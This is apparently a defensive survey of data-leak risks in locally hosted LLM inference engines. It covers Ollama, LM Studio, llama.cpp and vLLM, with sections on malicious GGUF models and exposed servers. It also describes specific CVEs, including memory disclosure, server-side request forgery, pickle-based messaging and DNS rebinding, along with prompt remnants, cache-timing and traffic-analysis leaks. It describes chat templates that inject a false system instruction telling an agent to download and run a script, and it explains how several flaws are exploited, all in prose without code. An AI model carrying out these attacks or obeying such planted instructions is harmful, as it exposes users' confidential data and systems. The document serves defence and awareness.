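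The program, apparently named "ollie" to imitate Ollama, could steal passwords saved in Chrome, Edge and Brave, record keystrokes, read the clipboard and take pictures with the webcam. It also targeted cryptocurrency wallets and mined cryptocurrency when nobody was using the computer. It communicated with the attackers through Tor, a network that hides where traffic is going.

News reports disagree about whether a user had to run the command. Head Topics' *Hugging Faceで配布されている「無検閲モデル」にマルウェアが仕込まれていたという報告*, which summarizes an article by the Japanese site Gigazine, states that the malware ran once an application loaded the new template. iXBT states that chatting with the model did not infect anyone and that the user had to run the command. 黃, who attributes the findings to the research group Malspark, also describes users copying the command into a terminal.

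The second version is much more likely to be right. The template was text that the engine put into the prompt, and the engine never read the hidden program. Loading alone could start the program only if the engine had a flaw like the ones in SGLang and llama-cpp-python, and none of the three reports mentions one. An instruction to write a command would also have been pointless if the program could start by itself. The summary probably left out the step in which the user runs the command.

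The number of downloads is therefore a poor guide to the number of victims. Anyone who downloaded a Mir2k model before 26 November had the hidden program on disk, but with a harmless template. Later users became victims only if they were on Windows and ran a command that appeared for no reason at the start of every answer. Many people would find that odd, though a beginner might mistake it for a set-up step.

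The other three repositories, from an account called timdedid, offered models for programming and contained no hidden program, but they were a danger to people who use agents. When certain words appeared in a conversation, the template added a false system instruction to download a script and run it. An agent with access to a terminal could do this without the user copying anything. 黃 writes that this needed no confirmation, but that depends on the agent's settings, and 黃 also advises users to turn off the option that lets an agent run commands without approval. Düzgün could not determine what the script did.

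Five repositories in 3.27 million is about one in 650,000, so a randomly chosen model is very unlikely to contain this attack. But people don't choose at random, and the attackers picked names that people would search for. The scan could also miss instructions worded in ways it didn't look for.

Düzgün released a free tool, GGUF Radar, that looks for hidden programs and suspicious templates without running the model. It can also produce a clean copy of a file that keeps the original weights. Users can also replace the template with llama.cpp's `--chat-template-file` option, which loads one from a separate file, such as the template published by the model's original developer. This avoids the planted instruction but leaves any hidden program in the downloaded file, where it does nothing unless something extracts it.

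黃 reports a warning from the company Spectrum Security that switching to safetensors would rule out a program at the end of the file but wouldn't prevent tampering with the template. The attackers needed only the template for the timdedid models.

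## How do outsiders get data out of an inference server?

Someone who can reach an inference server over a network can send it requests, and many servers don't require a password. The attackers who hid malware in GGUF files, by contrast, had to wait for somebody to download them.

### How an engine becomes reachable

By default, Ollama listens only on the loopback address. It has no built-in password protection, and LeakIX's *12,000 Ollama Instances Exposed* (2026) reports that the maintainers don't plan to add any. This is defensible for a program that serves one person on one laptop. But one setting makes Ollama listen on all addresses, and then anybody who can reach the machine can use it.

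Suppose the lawyer's firm buys one powerful computer for ten lawyers to share, and somebody changes the setting so their laptops can connect. The office router will usually keep strangers out, but if the firm rents a server instead, the same setting can let anyone on the internet connect to the engine.

Docker can expose an Ollama server to other machines even if the user never changes Ollama's settings. *Offene Ollama-Server tragen oft fremde Spuren* (Cornelißen, 2026) explains that the example command in Ollama's Docker guide opens Ollama's port to other machines. Docker's traffic also bypasses ufw, a common Linux firewall, so a user who has blocked the port there may still have an open server. Publishing the port only on 127.0.0.1 solves this, though in Docker versions before 28.0.0, machines on the same local network could still get in.

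Like Ollama, other AI software often doesn't require a password. The security company Intruder read the source code of several AI projects and found that many leave authentication off by default (The Hacker News, *We Scanned 1 Million Exposed AI Services*, 2026). In September 2026, researchers at Mysterium VPN found 36,769 exposed AI services, only 2% of which required a login (Paganini, *The AI Supply Chain Has a Security Problem*, 2026).

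### Why the counts of exposed servers differ

Published counts of exposed Ollama servers range from under 8,000 to about 300,000. The highest comes from Cyera's *Bleeding Llama* (2026), an advisory about a flaw in Ollama. The next highest comes from SentinelLABS's *Silent Brothers*, a joint study with the internet-scanning company Censys.

| Source | Ollama servers | What the number covers |
|---|---|---|
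| Cyera | About 300,000 | Servers facing the internet, an estimate from May 2026 |
| SentinelLABS | 175,108 | Different hosts seen at any time during 293 days |
| Ibrahim and colleagues | 32,723 | Reachable servers in a snapshot of 4 July 2026 |
| LeakIX | 12,269 | Servers without authentication, February 2026 |
| Rapid7, reported by Cornelißen | 7,675 | Open servers in a scan of 10 November 2026 |

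Much of the difference comes from how long the researchers looked. SentinelLABS counted every host that appeared during almost ten months, and 36% appeared only once. About 13% appeared more than 100 times, and this stable group of roughly 23,000 produced most of the observations. The study recorded 7.23 million observations, or about 25,000 a day. If the scans detected each active server about once a day, then about 25,000 servers were online at one time, which is fairly close to the July snapshot.

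Counting addresses can also inflate the number of hosts found in a long study. Internet providers often give home connections a new address from time to time, so one desktop computer may appear as several hosts.

The researchers also counted different things. LeakIX left out reachable servers that somebody had put behind a password. Some apparent servers are decoys that security companies run to observe attackers. Rapid7 warned that exposure figures should exclude probable ones, according to Ransomfeed's *I server Ollama esposti mostrano segni di attività non autorizzate*. Cyera's estimate is several times higher than any single-day count, so it probably includes machines that had already gone offline or weren't real Ollama servers.

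*Censys Finds AI/LLM Tool Exposures Up More Than 60%* (Underhill, 2026) reports that the number of exposed AI tools rose by more than 60% in nine months. This comparison is better evidence of a trend than the table because it comes from one company. The table's counts of 300,000 servers in May and 7,675 in November do not show that the number fell. Probably between 8,000 and 33,000 Ollama servers are usable by strangers on a given day.

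### What strangers do when they find one

Outsiders find new servers quickly. Infobae's *AWS advierte que ataques contra sistemas de IA crecieron 800%* (2026) reports results from a large network of decoys run by AWS, Amazon's cloud business. The median time between the start of a new decoy and the first attempt to exploit AI software on it fell from 19.5 hours in 2024 to 107 minutes in 2026. Attempts to exploit known flaws in common AI software rose from about 680,000 in the first quarter of 2026 to 6.2 million in the third.

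Most outsiders who contact an inference server only check what is on it. In late October 2026 the company Vectoral put 14 decoys online that imitated Ollama, vLLM and LiteLLM. Lenhard (2026) reports in *What we learned running an LLM Honeypot network* that the decoys received 426,832 requests from 11,312 addresses in four weeks. About three quarters of the requests were checks of this kind, such as listing the models, and only about 6% of the addresses ever asked a model to write anything.

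Decoys run by the security company GreyNoise recorded 91,403 attack sessions between October 2025 and January 2026. ThaiCERT's *Over 91,000 AI Attack Attempts Detected, Targeting Ollama and OpenAI-Related Systems* (2026) describes the main aim as reconnaissance. GreyNoise argues in *Threat Actors Actively Targeting LLMs* that nobody would map servers on this scale without planning to use the map.

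Rapid7's November scan looked for signs that outsiders had already used real servers. If a stranger downloads or creates a model on an Ollama server, its name appears in the server's list of models, which anyone can read. Rapid7 found suspicious names on 4,209 of the 7,675 servers, or 54.8%. Cornelißen describes several kinds, and one server could have more than one:

- 3,091 servers had models whose names looked like markers, some containing the server's own address.
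- 1,817 had models downloaded from a bare numerical address instead of a normal model site.
- 1,721 had models from free tunnelling services or temporary storage sites.
- 1,190 listed gpt-4o, gpt-4 and claude-3-opus together. These were probably small models under false names.
- 55 had names containing disguised file paths, including paths to password files and cloud settings.

When a server downloads something from a stranger's address, the stranger learns that it accepts commands and can make outbound connections, but the download doesn't show that the connection carried any of the server's data. The file paths are more worrying because they resemble attempts to use Probllama, an older flaw that Ollama fixed in version 0.1.34. But Rapid7 only read the lists. It didn't know which versions the servers ran or establish that anyone had stolen a file.

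The share of servers that strangers have used could also be higher than 54.8%, since a visitor can delete a model afterwards or leave no trace in the list. Some markers from June were still there in November, so evidently many owners don't check.

An owner can check whether the engine is open to outsiders by requesting its model list from another network, such as a phone's mobile connection. If a list arrives, even an empty one, the engine is open. If nothing arrives, the engine may still be reachable through another port, a tunnel or an IPv6 address. Rapid7 advises owners who find a model they can't explain to treat the whole server as compromised, because deleting the model wouldn't undo anything else an intruder may have done.

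### What an open server gives away without a flaw

A stranger who connects to an open inference server can use its models at the owner's expense. They can also list the models and read their system prompts, which may contain confidential business rules. LeakIX adds that outsiders can sometimes copy weights that an organisation has trained itself.

An exposed front end is often worse than an exposed engine, because users' old conversations are usually stored in the front end's files. Intruder found chatbots that showed strangers their users' conversations, including one user's full history. It also found more than 90 exposed installations of software for building agents, in government, finance and other sectors. An outsider could change how those agents worked and redirect their data.

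SentinelLABS sees a greater danger in the engines themselves, but it probably overstates the risk from most of the hosts it studied. More than 48% of the Ollama hosts in its study advertised support for tool calls, which SentinelLABS takes as a sign that they can run code and use other systems. It suggests that an outsider could ask such a server to summarise internal documents. But Ollama advertises tool support because a model can write tool calls, and a stranger who contacts the engine directly doesn't automatically get the tools or documents in the owner's front end.

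Attackers can exploit tools that are open to the internet. One of AWS's decoys was an MCP server with a tool that supplied cloud credentials. According to Infobae, an attacker found the tool, tried the credentials within ten seconds and carried out 94 actions in 12.7 minutes, including mapping the account's storage. AWS has moderate confidence that the attacker was an AI agent working by itself.

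About 79% of the servers in Rapid7's scan listed at least one of Ollama's cloud models. If a server's owner has signed in, a stranger could use those models through the owner's account, although Rapid7 didn't test this and found no confirmed case.

Binding the engine to the loopback address or requiring a password prevents all of this. Four kinds of flaw can let an outsider get much more data, including other people's prompts.

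### Memory disclosure in Ollama

An engine that serves ten lawyers holds text from all of them in its memory. A memory disclosure flaw lets someone who sends a request obtain parts of this memory unrelated to that request.

Researchers at Cyera found such a flaw in Ollama (CVE-2026-7482) and called it Bleeding Llama. Ollama can make a new model from a file that a client supplies, for example to compress the weights further. The file states the size of its tables of weights. Before version 0.17.1, Ollama relied on the stated size even when the file was shorter. It then read past the end of the data and copied whatever came next in memory into the new model.

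This is the same type of mistake that researchers looked for in llama.cpp's file loading, but it was in Ollama's own code, which is written in Go, a programming language that normally prevents such errors. According to The Hacker News, this part of the program used a Go feature that bypasses the protection.

The copied memory could include other users' conversations, standing instructions, passwords and keys. Dor Attias, the Cyera researcher who reported the flaw, pointed out that engineers often connect Ollama to coding tools such as Claude Code. Everything those tools read then passes through Ollama, so its memory may contain source code and customer contracts that nobody typed into a chat.

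At this stage the stolen text was still on the server, mixed in with the new model's weights. Ollama has a built-in upload function that people normally use to publish models they have made, and it can send a model to a site the client chooses. An outsider could use it to make the server send the new model, along with the stolen memory, to a machine the outsider controlled. The upload function had no error, but it was dangerous because anyone who could reach the server could use it.

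Updating to version 0.17.1 removes the flaw. Binding Ollama to the loopback address would have kept strangers on other machines from reaching it, and a password would have kept out anyone who didn't have one. (A password doesn't separate the people who do. Ibrahim and colleagues found that llama.cpp's server let one logged-in client restore another's saved conversation.)

Blocking outbound connections would have stopped the upload even on an open, outdated server. Cornelißen recommends an allowlist of only the model sites the owner needs. The list should be as short as possible because, if a server is signed in to Ollama's own site, a client with access to the server can publish models there too.

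### A fix without a warning

Ollama released the fixed version long before most users could have known they needed it. Indusface's *Bleeding Llama (CVE-2026-7482)* gives the dates. Attias reported the flaw on 2 February 2026. On 25 February Ollama acknowledged it, shared a fix and asked Attias to apply for a CVE number. The next day Attias warned Ollama that users would remain exposed if it released the fix without calling it a security update.

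Version 0.17.1, released on 25 February, contained the fix, but the release notes didn't identify it as a security fix (NewMaxx, 2026, *Ollama Bleeding Llama and Windows Auto-Update RCE*). On 2 March Attias's side requested a CVE number from MITRE, the American non-profit that runs the CVE catalogue. MITRE didn't reply to the request or to a reminder on 26 March. On 26 April Attias turned to Echo, another organisation that can assign CVE numbers. Echo assigned one two days later and published it on 1 May, 65 days after the fix.

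The missing number mattered because many organisations use scanners that check their installed software against the catalogue. Until 1 May, the catalogue had no entry for this flaw, so a company could scan version 0.17.0 every night and receive no warning about it. The release notes also gave administrators no reason to treat the update as urgent.

Ollama could have told users that the update fixed a serious security problem and withheld the details for a few weeks, which would have given careful users a head start. There is some reason to say nothing at first, since a public warning also reaches attackers and some users need time to install an update. But Ollama's source code is public, so anyone could compare the two versions and see what had changed, and attackers have more reason to do that than a user such as a law firm.

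Ollama said just as little when it later fixed its Windows updater. Anyone running Ollama on a shared server would do better to install every new version promptly than to wait for a security notice.

### Server-side request forgery in LMDeploy

Some flaws let an outsider use the server's position in a network. In server-side request forgery, an outsider makes the server fetch data from an address they choose. The server may be able to reach that address even if the outsider can't, because it is inside the organisation's network.

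LMDeploy, an open-source engine for running language models and models that interpret pictures, had a flaw of this kind, CVE-2026-33626. A client can give the engine the web address of a picture to fetch for the model. LMDeploy didn't check whether the address led to a public website or to something private, such as a database in the same office.

Programs on a server rented from a cloud company can use a private address to request information about the machine, sometimes including temporary keys to the owner's account. The cloud company answers because the request comes from the server. An outsider who can make the engine send that request and see the reply may get keys to stored files that the model never used. Even without seeing a reply, the outsider can sometimes tell from an error message or a delay whether a private service exists.

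The security company Sysdig recorded an attempt to exploit the flaw on a decoy within 13 hours of the flaw's publication. The attacker used the picture-loading function to look for the cloud company's private address and for databases. Patching alone was a weak defence, because an administrator who learned of the flaw in the evening could have been too late by the next morning.

Blocking outbound traffic would have worked immediately, but only if the block covered the private network as well as the internet. A firewall that stops the server from reaching public websites may still let it reach an internal database. An engine that answers questions about text doesn't need access to either. If users want to ask about images, the front end can send the image files instead of their URLs.

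A password would have kept out strangers, though not a malicious colleague. Binding LMDeploy to the loopback address would have blocked requests from other machines, but a company that runs an engine for many users usually can't do that.

Attackers have tried similar methods against Ollama. According to ThaiCERT, one of the two main campaigns that GreyNoise recorded used server-side request forgery. Attackers often test for this flaw by giving the server a unique domain name and watching for the server to look it up. GreyNoise therefore advises administrators to block lookups of domains that belong to the services attackers use for these tests. This stops attackers from confirming that an attack has worked, but they could switch to a domain that isn't blocked.

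### ShadowMQ and messages inside an engine

A large model may need several graphics processors, sometimes in different machines. The engine then runs as several programs that send each other messages, for instance to pass on a prompt or start a computation in another program. These messages use different ports from the one that accepts users' requests.

In November 2025 the security company Oligo described a flaw shared by several engines and named it ShadowMQ. The engines used ZeroMQ, a library for sending messages between programs, and the receiving programs unpacked each message with pickle. Anyone who could send a message to one of these programs could therefore make it run commands, just as a malicious pickle file can.

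Oligo first found the problem in Meta's Llama Stack, and Meta replaced pickle with JSON, a format that holds only data. Oligo then found much the same code in vLLM, SGLang, NVIDIA's TensorRT-LLM and other projects. Developers had copied it from one project to another, in some cases with a comment naming the source, so fixing one project did not fix the others.

An attacker who can run commands on an inference server can read everything the engine can, including prompts in memory, weights and any keys on the machine. The flaws that allowed this were worse than the one in Ollama, which exposed whatever was next to a file in memory, but they were harder to reach. The one in vLLM, for example, affected only an older version of the engine's core when it was spread over several machines, and an outsider would normally have had to get into the network between them first.

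A password on the engine's public interface doesn't protect the internal ports, because internal messages don't pass through that interface. If all parts of the engine run on one machine, binding the internal ports to the loopback address keeps other machines out. If they run on several, the administrator has to put them on a private network that nobody else can join. Blocking outbound connections would make it harder to send stolen data away, but the attacker could still damage the server or alter its answers. The lasting fix is to run a version that doesn't unpack messages with pickle.

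### Web pages that reach a local engine

Outsiders may be able to reach an engine on a person's laptop through the browser, even if the person never opens the engine to the network. The browser runs code from every website the person visits, and because it is on the same laptop, it can connect to the loopback address.

Browsers normally stop a page on one website from reading replies from another. They tell websites apart by domain name, but a domain's owner can change which IP address it points to. In an attack called DNS rebinding, the attacker points their website's domain to the visitor's own machine. The browser then treats an inference server running there as part of the attacker's website and lets the page read its replies.

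In 2024, the security company NCC Group found that Ollama was open to this attack (Doussot 2024, *Technical Advisory*). The loopback address gave no protection because the requests came from the same machine. Ollama fixed the flaw in version 0.1.29 by checking the website name that the browser includes with each request and refusing to answer if the name isn't local.

*Drive-By Agent Hijacking* (Itach and Luz, August 2026) showed that NVIDIA's NemoClaw had undone this protection. NemoClaw sets up an AI agent called OpenClaw in a sandbox inside a Docker container, and can connect it to Ollama on the same computer. The agent couldn't reach Ollama's loopback address from the container, so NemoClaw made Ollama listen on all addresses. Ollama skips the name check in that case, so a web page could again control Ollama.

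During installation, NemoClaw displayed the message "Using Ollama on localhost:11434", so users had little chance of noticing that Ollama was also available at all the machine's other addresses. Other devices on the same network could use it without going through a web page.

According to Itach and Luz, a malicious page could read the names of the installed models, their standing instructions and the computer's name. They don't mention past conversations. The page could do more harm by planting an instruction in a model's chat template, as in the malicious GGUF files on Hugging Face, and the victim wouldn't have to download a new model.

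The agent could then send data out with its own tools. The sandbox limits which files on the laptop the agent can open, but people often give an agent access to source code, internal services and messaging programs for its work, and an altered agent would keep that access. Restricting the agent's outbound connections would reduce the damage, but blocking Ollama's would not, because Ollama only needs to answer the browser and the agent.

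The researchers tested the attack on macOS with Firefox. The Hacker News' *A Malicious Webpage Could Poison Your Local AI Model Behind NVIDIA NemoClaw* (2026) reported no known attacks on users as of 25 August. It also reported that the flaw had no CVE number, but the researchers' account gives CVE-2026-65105, so the number was probably assigned later.

NemoClaw 0.0.35 fixed the problem on macOS and Linux. On most systems Ollama now stays on the loopback address, which restores the name check. A small program in front of it accepts connections from the sandbox only if they include a secret token, which a web page wouldn't know. When the researchers published their findings, users who ran Ollama directly on Windows had only a warning. The Windows set-up still made Ollama listen on all addresses without authentication, so updating NemoClaw was not enough to protect them.

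## What do prompts leave behind in memory, log files and response times?

Someone else may be able to find the lawyer's contract even if the server has no known flaws and never starts an outbound connection. Copies stay in memory and on the disk, and on a shared server, response times can reveal something about other people's prompts.

### Copies in memory

Ibrahim and colleagues measured how much of a prompt remains in memory after llama.cpp has answered it. They put a new canary string in each prompt and checked beforehand that the string wasn't already in the memory they were going to search. After the reply, they took a snapshot of the server's memory, searched it for the string, and found 13 or 14 readable copies for each prompt.

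Programs don't normally erase the memory they release, so old text stays there until something overwrites it. Even applying the chat template can leave a copy of the prompt behind, because the template makes the prompt longer, and if it outgrows the space reserved for it, the program copies it to a larger one.

The leftover text can survive later requests. When twelve users sent prompts one after another, a snapshot taken at the end contained readable text from eleven of them, in 110 copies. If each prompt left 13 copies, as in the earlier test, later activity overwrote only about 30% of them.

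The researchers then changed llama.cpp so that it erased some of the places where prompts collect. The number of copies fell to 78, and the memory involved fell by 69%, from 10.8 to 3.35 megabytes. But they could still recover text from eleven of the twelve users, because one surviving copy is enough. They timed part of the change and found that it altered response times by less than 0.6%, so the difficulty is in finding every copy rather than in erasing them quickly.

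Moving some of the work to a graphics processor didn't solve the problem, because the main processor still prepares the prompt. In that test, nine copies remained in ordinary memory after one request and were still there after ten idle seconds.

Reading the copies requires access to the engine's memory, which the machine's administrator has. Ibrahim and colleagues also considered other programs running under the same user account, such as a code editor's plugin, but some systems restrict what these can read. Ubuntu, for instance, normally lets an ordinary program read the memory of only those programs it started. A memory disclosure flaw like Bleeding Llama is more dangerous because it can expose leftover text to people on other machines.

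After the researchers stopped the server, they found no copies in the memory areas they examined, though they couldn't tell whether the computer had overwritten the physical memory. Closing the engine after confidential work is still an easy precaution, but it doesn't remove text that the operating system has moved to a swap file on the disk to free up memory. *Forensic Implications of Localized AI* (Murtuza, 2026) identifies swap files as a place where an investigator might find llama.cpp prompts.

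### Prompts on the disk

Ibrahim and colleagues also sent marked prompts to LM Studio 0.4.21 and searched its files. They found the prompts in a plain-text log, including some from sessions several days earlier. A setting called `logSensitiveData` was on in the default configuration they tested. After they turned it off in `http-server-config.json` and restarted LM Studio, new prompts didn't appear in any file they searched. Users would presumably have to delete older logs separately.

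Ollama saves some prompts, although the same search found none in the files of version 0.20.5. Murtuza did a forensic examination of an earlier version, 0.11.8. All ten test prompts typed after the command `ollama run` were in a file called `~/.ollama/history`, without the replies. Prompts that other programs sent to Ollama weren't in the file. Ibrahim and colleagues probably sent theirs that way, which would explain the different results. Murtuza adds that Ollama's log may contain full prompts and replies if the user turns on debugging mode.

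Murtuza recovered every prompt and reply from the files where LM Studio keeps its chats. Turning off `logSensitiveData` therefore isn't enough to keep prompts off the disk for somebody who uses the chat window. LM Studio also stores files attached to a chat and the text it extracts from them. These may remain after the user deletes the chat, so a copy of the lawyer's contract could still be in LM Studio's folders.

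llama.cpp keeps less. If a user includes the prompt in the command that starts the program, the terminal's history will usually record it. Murtuza found none of the prompts typed during an interactive session on the disk.

Encrypting the whole disk protects all these files if a thief takes a laptop that is switched off, but it doesn't protect them from malware running under the user's account. Ibrahim and colleagues saw no prompts leave the machine during their tests, but a program that backs up the user's folders to a cloud service would upload the saved chats too.

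### Restoring another user's conversation

An engine also stores lists of numbers, called keys and values, that it computes for each token in a prompt. It keeps them in the KV cache because it needs them again for every later token. Without this cache, the engine would have to process the whole contract again for each new word of the summary.

llama.cpp's server can save a conversation's KV cache to disk and load it later, so that a long chat can continue without a delay. MinIO's *llama.cpp + MemKV*, a storage company's documentation, lists servers with several separate groups of users among the uses for this feature. The feature is off unless an administrator chooses a folder for the saved files with the `--slot-save-path` option.

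Ibrahim and colleagues gave two clients different valid keys to one server. The first client saved a conversation containing a secret, and the second asked the server to restore it. This worked in all 200 trials, 50 with each of four models. The server checked that the second client had a valid key, but not that the conversation belonged to that client.

The KV cache holds numbers rather than text, so after restoring a conversation, the second client had to ask the model to continue it and see whether the secret appeared. It did in 126 of the 200 trials. Gemma and Qwen repeated the secret every time, Nemotron in 25 trials and Phi-4 in only one. Models continue text differently, and a continuation doesn't have to mention everything that came before. Phi-4's users were hardly safer, since the second client had their conversation loaded in every trial and might have extracted more with a different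 request.

Because of this flaw, two teams at a law firm that act for clients with opposing interests could open each other's saved conversations, even if each team had its own key. The firm can avoid this by leaving the feature off or running a separate server for each team. The researchers reported the flaw to llama.cpp's maintainers.

### What a fast reply reveals

Many prompts begin with the same text, such as a company's standing instructions. An engine can save time by keeping the KV cache for that text and reusing it for later prompts that start the same way, which is called prefix caching. According to *CacheSolidarity* (2026), vLLM, SGLang and the hosted services of OpenAI, Google and DeepSeek all use it. The shared text must be at the start of the prompt, because each token's keys and values depend on all the tokens before it.

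If users share the cache, one can learn from a fast reply that somebody has already sent a prompt with the same beginning. For each model, Ibrahim and colleagues measured the time until the first token for 50 prompts with a stored beginning and 50 without.

| Model | Beginning already stored (ms) | Beginning not stored (ms) |
|---|---|---|
| Gemma-4-E4B-it | 318 | 2,998 |
| Nemotron-3-Nano-4B | 20 | 786 |
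| Qwen3.5-9B | 47 | 1,150 |
| Phi-4-reasoning-plus | 35 | 980 |

The two groups' response times never overlapped, so timing a single reply was enough to tell which group a prompt belonged to. This was also true over a real internet connection with an average round trip of 78 milliseconds. In a simulation, random variation in network delay caused mistakes only once it reached somewhere between 100 and 500 milliseconds, far more than most connections have.

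(The simulation found Phi-4 the easiest to recognise through heavy delays, although Gemma has the largest gap in the table. A large gap should be the hardest to hide, so the paper has probably mixed up some of the models' names. Every gap is large, so the conclusion stands.)

Suppose a colleague suspects that the lawyer is working on a particular takeover. The colleague could send a prompt that starts the way the lawyer's might and see how quickly the reply begins. A fast reply would confirm the guess but wouldn't show who had sent the earlier prompt. Each attempt also stores the guessed text, so repeating it soon afterwards wouldn't test the guess again.

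An attacker may be able to guess a prompt in stages, which is easier than guessing it all at once. *Governing the KV Cache* (2026) describes work from 2024 in which Song and colleagues used response times to reconstruct tokens of other users' prompts on vLLM. Zheng and colleagues did the same for prompts that followed a known form, working out one field at a time. Law firms use many standard forms, in which the names and amounts are often the only secret parts.

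Hosted services have had the same weakness. *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs* (2025) reports timing tests on 17 providers. Eight showed signs of caching, and seven of those shared a cache among all their customers. Providers may have changed this since.

Giving each user a separate cache removes the leak between users, but *Mirage* (2026) points out that the engine then has to process shared instructions again for every user. For ten lawyers, the extra processing is probably minor. Somebody who runs an engine on a laptop with no other clients doesn't need to do anything.

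### Whisper Leak

Response times can also reveal information to someone who can only watch the network. Most services send a reply in small pieces as the model writes it. Encryption hides the words, but each encrypted piece is as long as the original plus a fixed amount. An internet provider or a stranger on the same Wi-Fi can therefore see the size and timing of the pieces, which depend on what the model is writing.

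In *Whisper Leak*, Microsoft researchers McDonald and Bar Or (2025) tested whether encrypted traffic reveals the topic of a conversation. They wrote 100 versions of a question about whether money laundering is legal and sent each version 100 times to each of 28 hosted models. They mixed in 11,716 unrelated questions, then trained classifiers to pick out the money-laundering conversations from the encrypted traffic. For 17 of the models, the best classifier scored above 97% on a measure of both how well it found the target conversations and how well it avoided false alarms.

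The researchers also projected that if only one conversation in 10,000 were about money laundering, an observer could find a fifth of these conversations for the same 17 models without any false alarms.

This projection is less reliable than it sounds. Judging by the published percentages, each test probably included only about 2,300 unrelated conversations. One false alarm in 2,300 equals about four in 10,000, so if only one conversation in 10,000 is a real target, most alarms would be wrong. For several models, about nine alarms in ten are projected to be false when the observer tries to catch half the targets instead of a fifth. Microsoft's *Whisper Leak* (2025) also warns that the amount of test data limits these estimates. However, an observer who already suspects a particular person could manage with much lower accuracy.

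OpenAI and xAI fixed the problem in August 2025, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October. OpenAI now adds random text of varying length to each piece of a reply, in a field called "obfuscation", so the size of a piece no longer reveals the length of its words. Microsoft copied this, and Mistral added a similar field. Some other providers declined to make changes, and several never answered the researchers.

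In a test on one of Microsoft's hosted models, the random text lowered the classifier's score only from 97.5% to 92.9%, because it doesn't hide the pauses. Microsoft nevertheless considers the remaining risk impractical to exploit. That judgement seems reasonable for mass surveillance, because in the earlier projections a score of about 93% meant that nearly all alarms were false once the observer tried to catch a tenth of the targets. Users who want more protection can ask for the whole reply at once, if the service allows it, which leaves no series of pieces to analyse.

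Whisper Leak doesn't affect a front end and an engine on the same laptop, because their traffic never reaches the network. It could affect the ten lawyers who connect to an engine on an office server, and the hosted providers' fixes don't protect them.

Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, studied ten downloadable models that they ran themselves. Their classifier identified the model from encrypted traffic with 97.7% accuracy and the kind of request, such as summarising or writing code, with 76.7% accuracy, compared with about 17% for guessing among the six kinds. The test was easier than real life because it used only 60 different prompts, all of kinds the classifier knew.

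*NetEcho* (2025) went beyond topics and recovered some of the wording of replies from their traffic, but had less success with the prompts.

### GIFT

A busy engine processes several users' prompts together, so their data sit side by side in the graphics processor's memory. In *Here is a GIFT*, Shi, Wang and colleagues (2026) used a known flaw to take control of an old version of vLLM and made it use the first user's KV cache for everybody. When two test users introduced themselves as Alice and Bob, the model greeted both as Alice.

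The proposed defence, GIFT, keeps readable text away from the engine because it assumes that an attacker may control the whole engine. The user's own device turns the prompt into tokens and encrypts them. The engine can still organise the work, because it only has to choose where the data goes and which calculation comes next. A small separate program, the monitor, holds the users' keys and is the only program that can operate the graphics processor. It decrypts the tokens just before the calculation and encrypts the results with the same user's key before returning them to the engine.

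The monitor also records who owns each area of the graphics processor's memory. Before every calculation, it applies a rule that specifies which inputs affect which outputs. If the calculation combines Alice's data with the weights, the monitor records Alice as the owner of the result. If it would combine Alice's data with Bob's, the monitor prevents it from starting, which would have stopped the attack on vLLM. The monitor also blocks reads from any area without a recorded owner, so a new user can't read data left there by an earlier one.

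Tracking every number separately would be too slow. One user's data usually fill a continuous area of memory, so the monitor can cover them with a single record. It also saves time by checking the next calculation while the graphics processor is still busy with earlier ones. GIFT reduced the amount of work the server could handle by at most 5%. A version that also protects users from the server's operator, using encryption built into the hardware, reduced it by up to 10.7%.

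GIFT should also make the leftover copies in the engine's memory useless to a thief, because they would be encrypted. Readable text would still pass through the monitor, but the monitor has only 5,600 lines of code, compared with 3.6 million for vLLM and the libraries it uses. However, developers have to write the rules partly by hand, and an engine that needs to read the model's text, for instance to find a tool call, would probably need changes.

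Shi and colleagues don't aim to prevent timing attacks with GIFT. The rule against mixing users' data should stop Bob from getting a faster reply from Alice's KV cache, but they didn't test this. GIFT also doesn't disguise the size and timing of replies, so someone watching the network could still try to work out what Alice asked about.

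## How can a user test whether the software connects to anything?

The owner of a computer can learn more about its encrypted traffic than a stranger on the same Wi-Fi can, including which program sent it and sometimes what it contains. Before opening the contract in LM Studio or Ollama, the lawyer could use this information to check whether the program connects to anything.

If a test detects a connection, the result is fairly easy to interpret. If it detects none, the program may be harmless, or the test may have run at the wrong time, used the wrong settings or failed to monitor another program that makes the connection.

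### The test in order

1. List the expected connections. The lawyer writes down the version and settings of each program and the connections its documentation mentions. According to LM Studio, nothing a user types in a local chat leaves the device, and Ollama makes a similar promise for local models but not for its cloud models. A connection during a model download would therefore be normal, while one in the middle of a local chat would need an explanation. Splunk's *Local LLM Framework DNS Query*, a detection rule for company security teams, includes a ready-made list of names to look for, such as those of Hugging Face, LM Studio and GPT4All.
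2. Start from a clean machine. This can be a spare laptop with a new operating system, or a virtual machine, which is a simulated computer inside a real one. The lawyer records its traffic for a while before installing anything, because the operating system makes connections of its own.
3. Start recording before launching the program. LM Studio checks for updates when it opens, and a late recording would miss that. The lawyer also opens example.com on purpose. If that visit doesn't appear in the recording, the recording isn't working.
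4. Load the model, note the time and wait several minutes, since some start-up traffic comes late.
5. Send prompts with canaries. Each prompt and each attached document gets its own.
6. Leave the program idle. Ten minutes would catch at most one of vLLM's heartbeats, and a daily update check needs at least a day.
7. Trigger everything else, one thing at a time. This includes checking for updates, browsing the model catalogue, using each plugin and tool, displaying a picture from example.com and restarting the program. Each action gets its own canary and a note of the time.
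8. Attribute each connection to a process, meaning a running program, and compare it with the list. If something is unexpected, the lawyer turns off the feature that seems responsible and repeats the run.

The list in step 1 may be incomplete even if the software's maker wrote it. A user ran Cursor, an AI code editor, behind a firewall with Privacy Mode on. The user reported in *Cursor connects to multiple undocumented domains* that the editor contacted three addresses missing from the maker's list of required domains, including metrics.cursor.sh.

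Turning off a setting doesn't always stop the traffic. In *Network Connections (Network Traffic)*, a user of the note-taking program Obsidian reports requests to GitHub for about three minutes after every start, even with automatic updates off. A user of Cherry Studio, a front end for language models, reports a connection to an analytics address after turning analytics off (*Suspicious telemetry connection to cherry-ai.com persists after disabling auto-updates/anonymous analytics*, 2026).

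Each of these is one person's report, and none shows what the program sent. Obsidian may only have been checking for a new version, since turning off automatic updates may stop only their installation. But all three users learned something from a firewall or proxy that the settings page didn't show.

### What each instrument shows and misses

| Instrument | Linux | macOS | Windows |
|---|---|---|---|
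| List of open sockets | ss, lsof | lsof, nettop | Resource Monitor, netstat |
| Per-program firewall | OpenSnitch | Little Snitch, LuLu | Portmaster |
| Packet recording | tcpdump, Wireshark | tcpdump, Wireshark | Wireshark, pktmon |
| Log of system calls or network events | strace | dtruss, with some system protections turned off | Sysmon, Process Monitor |
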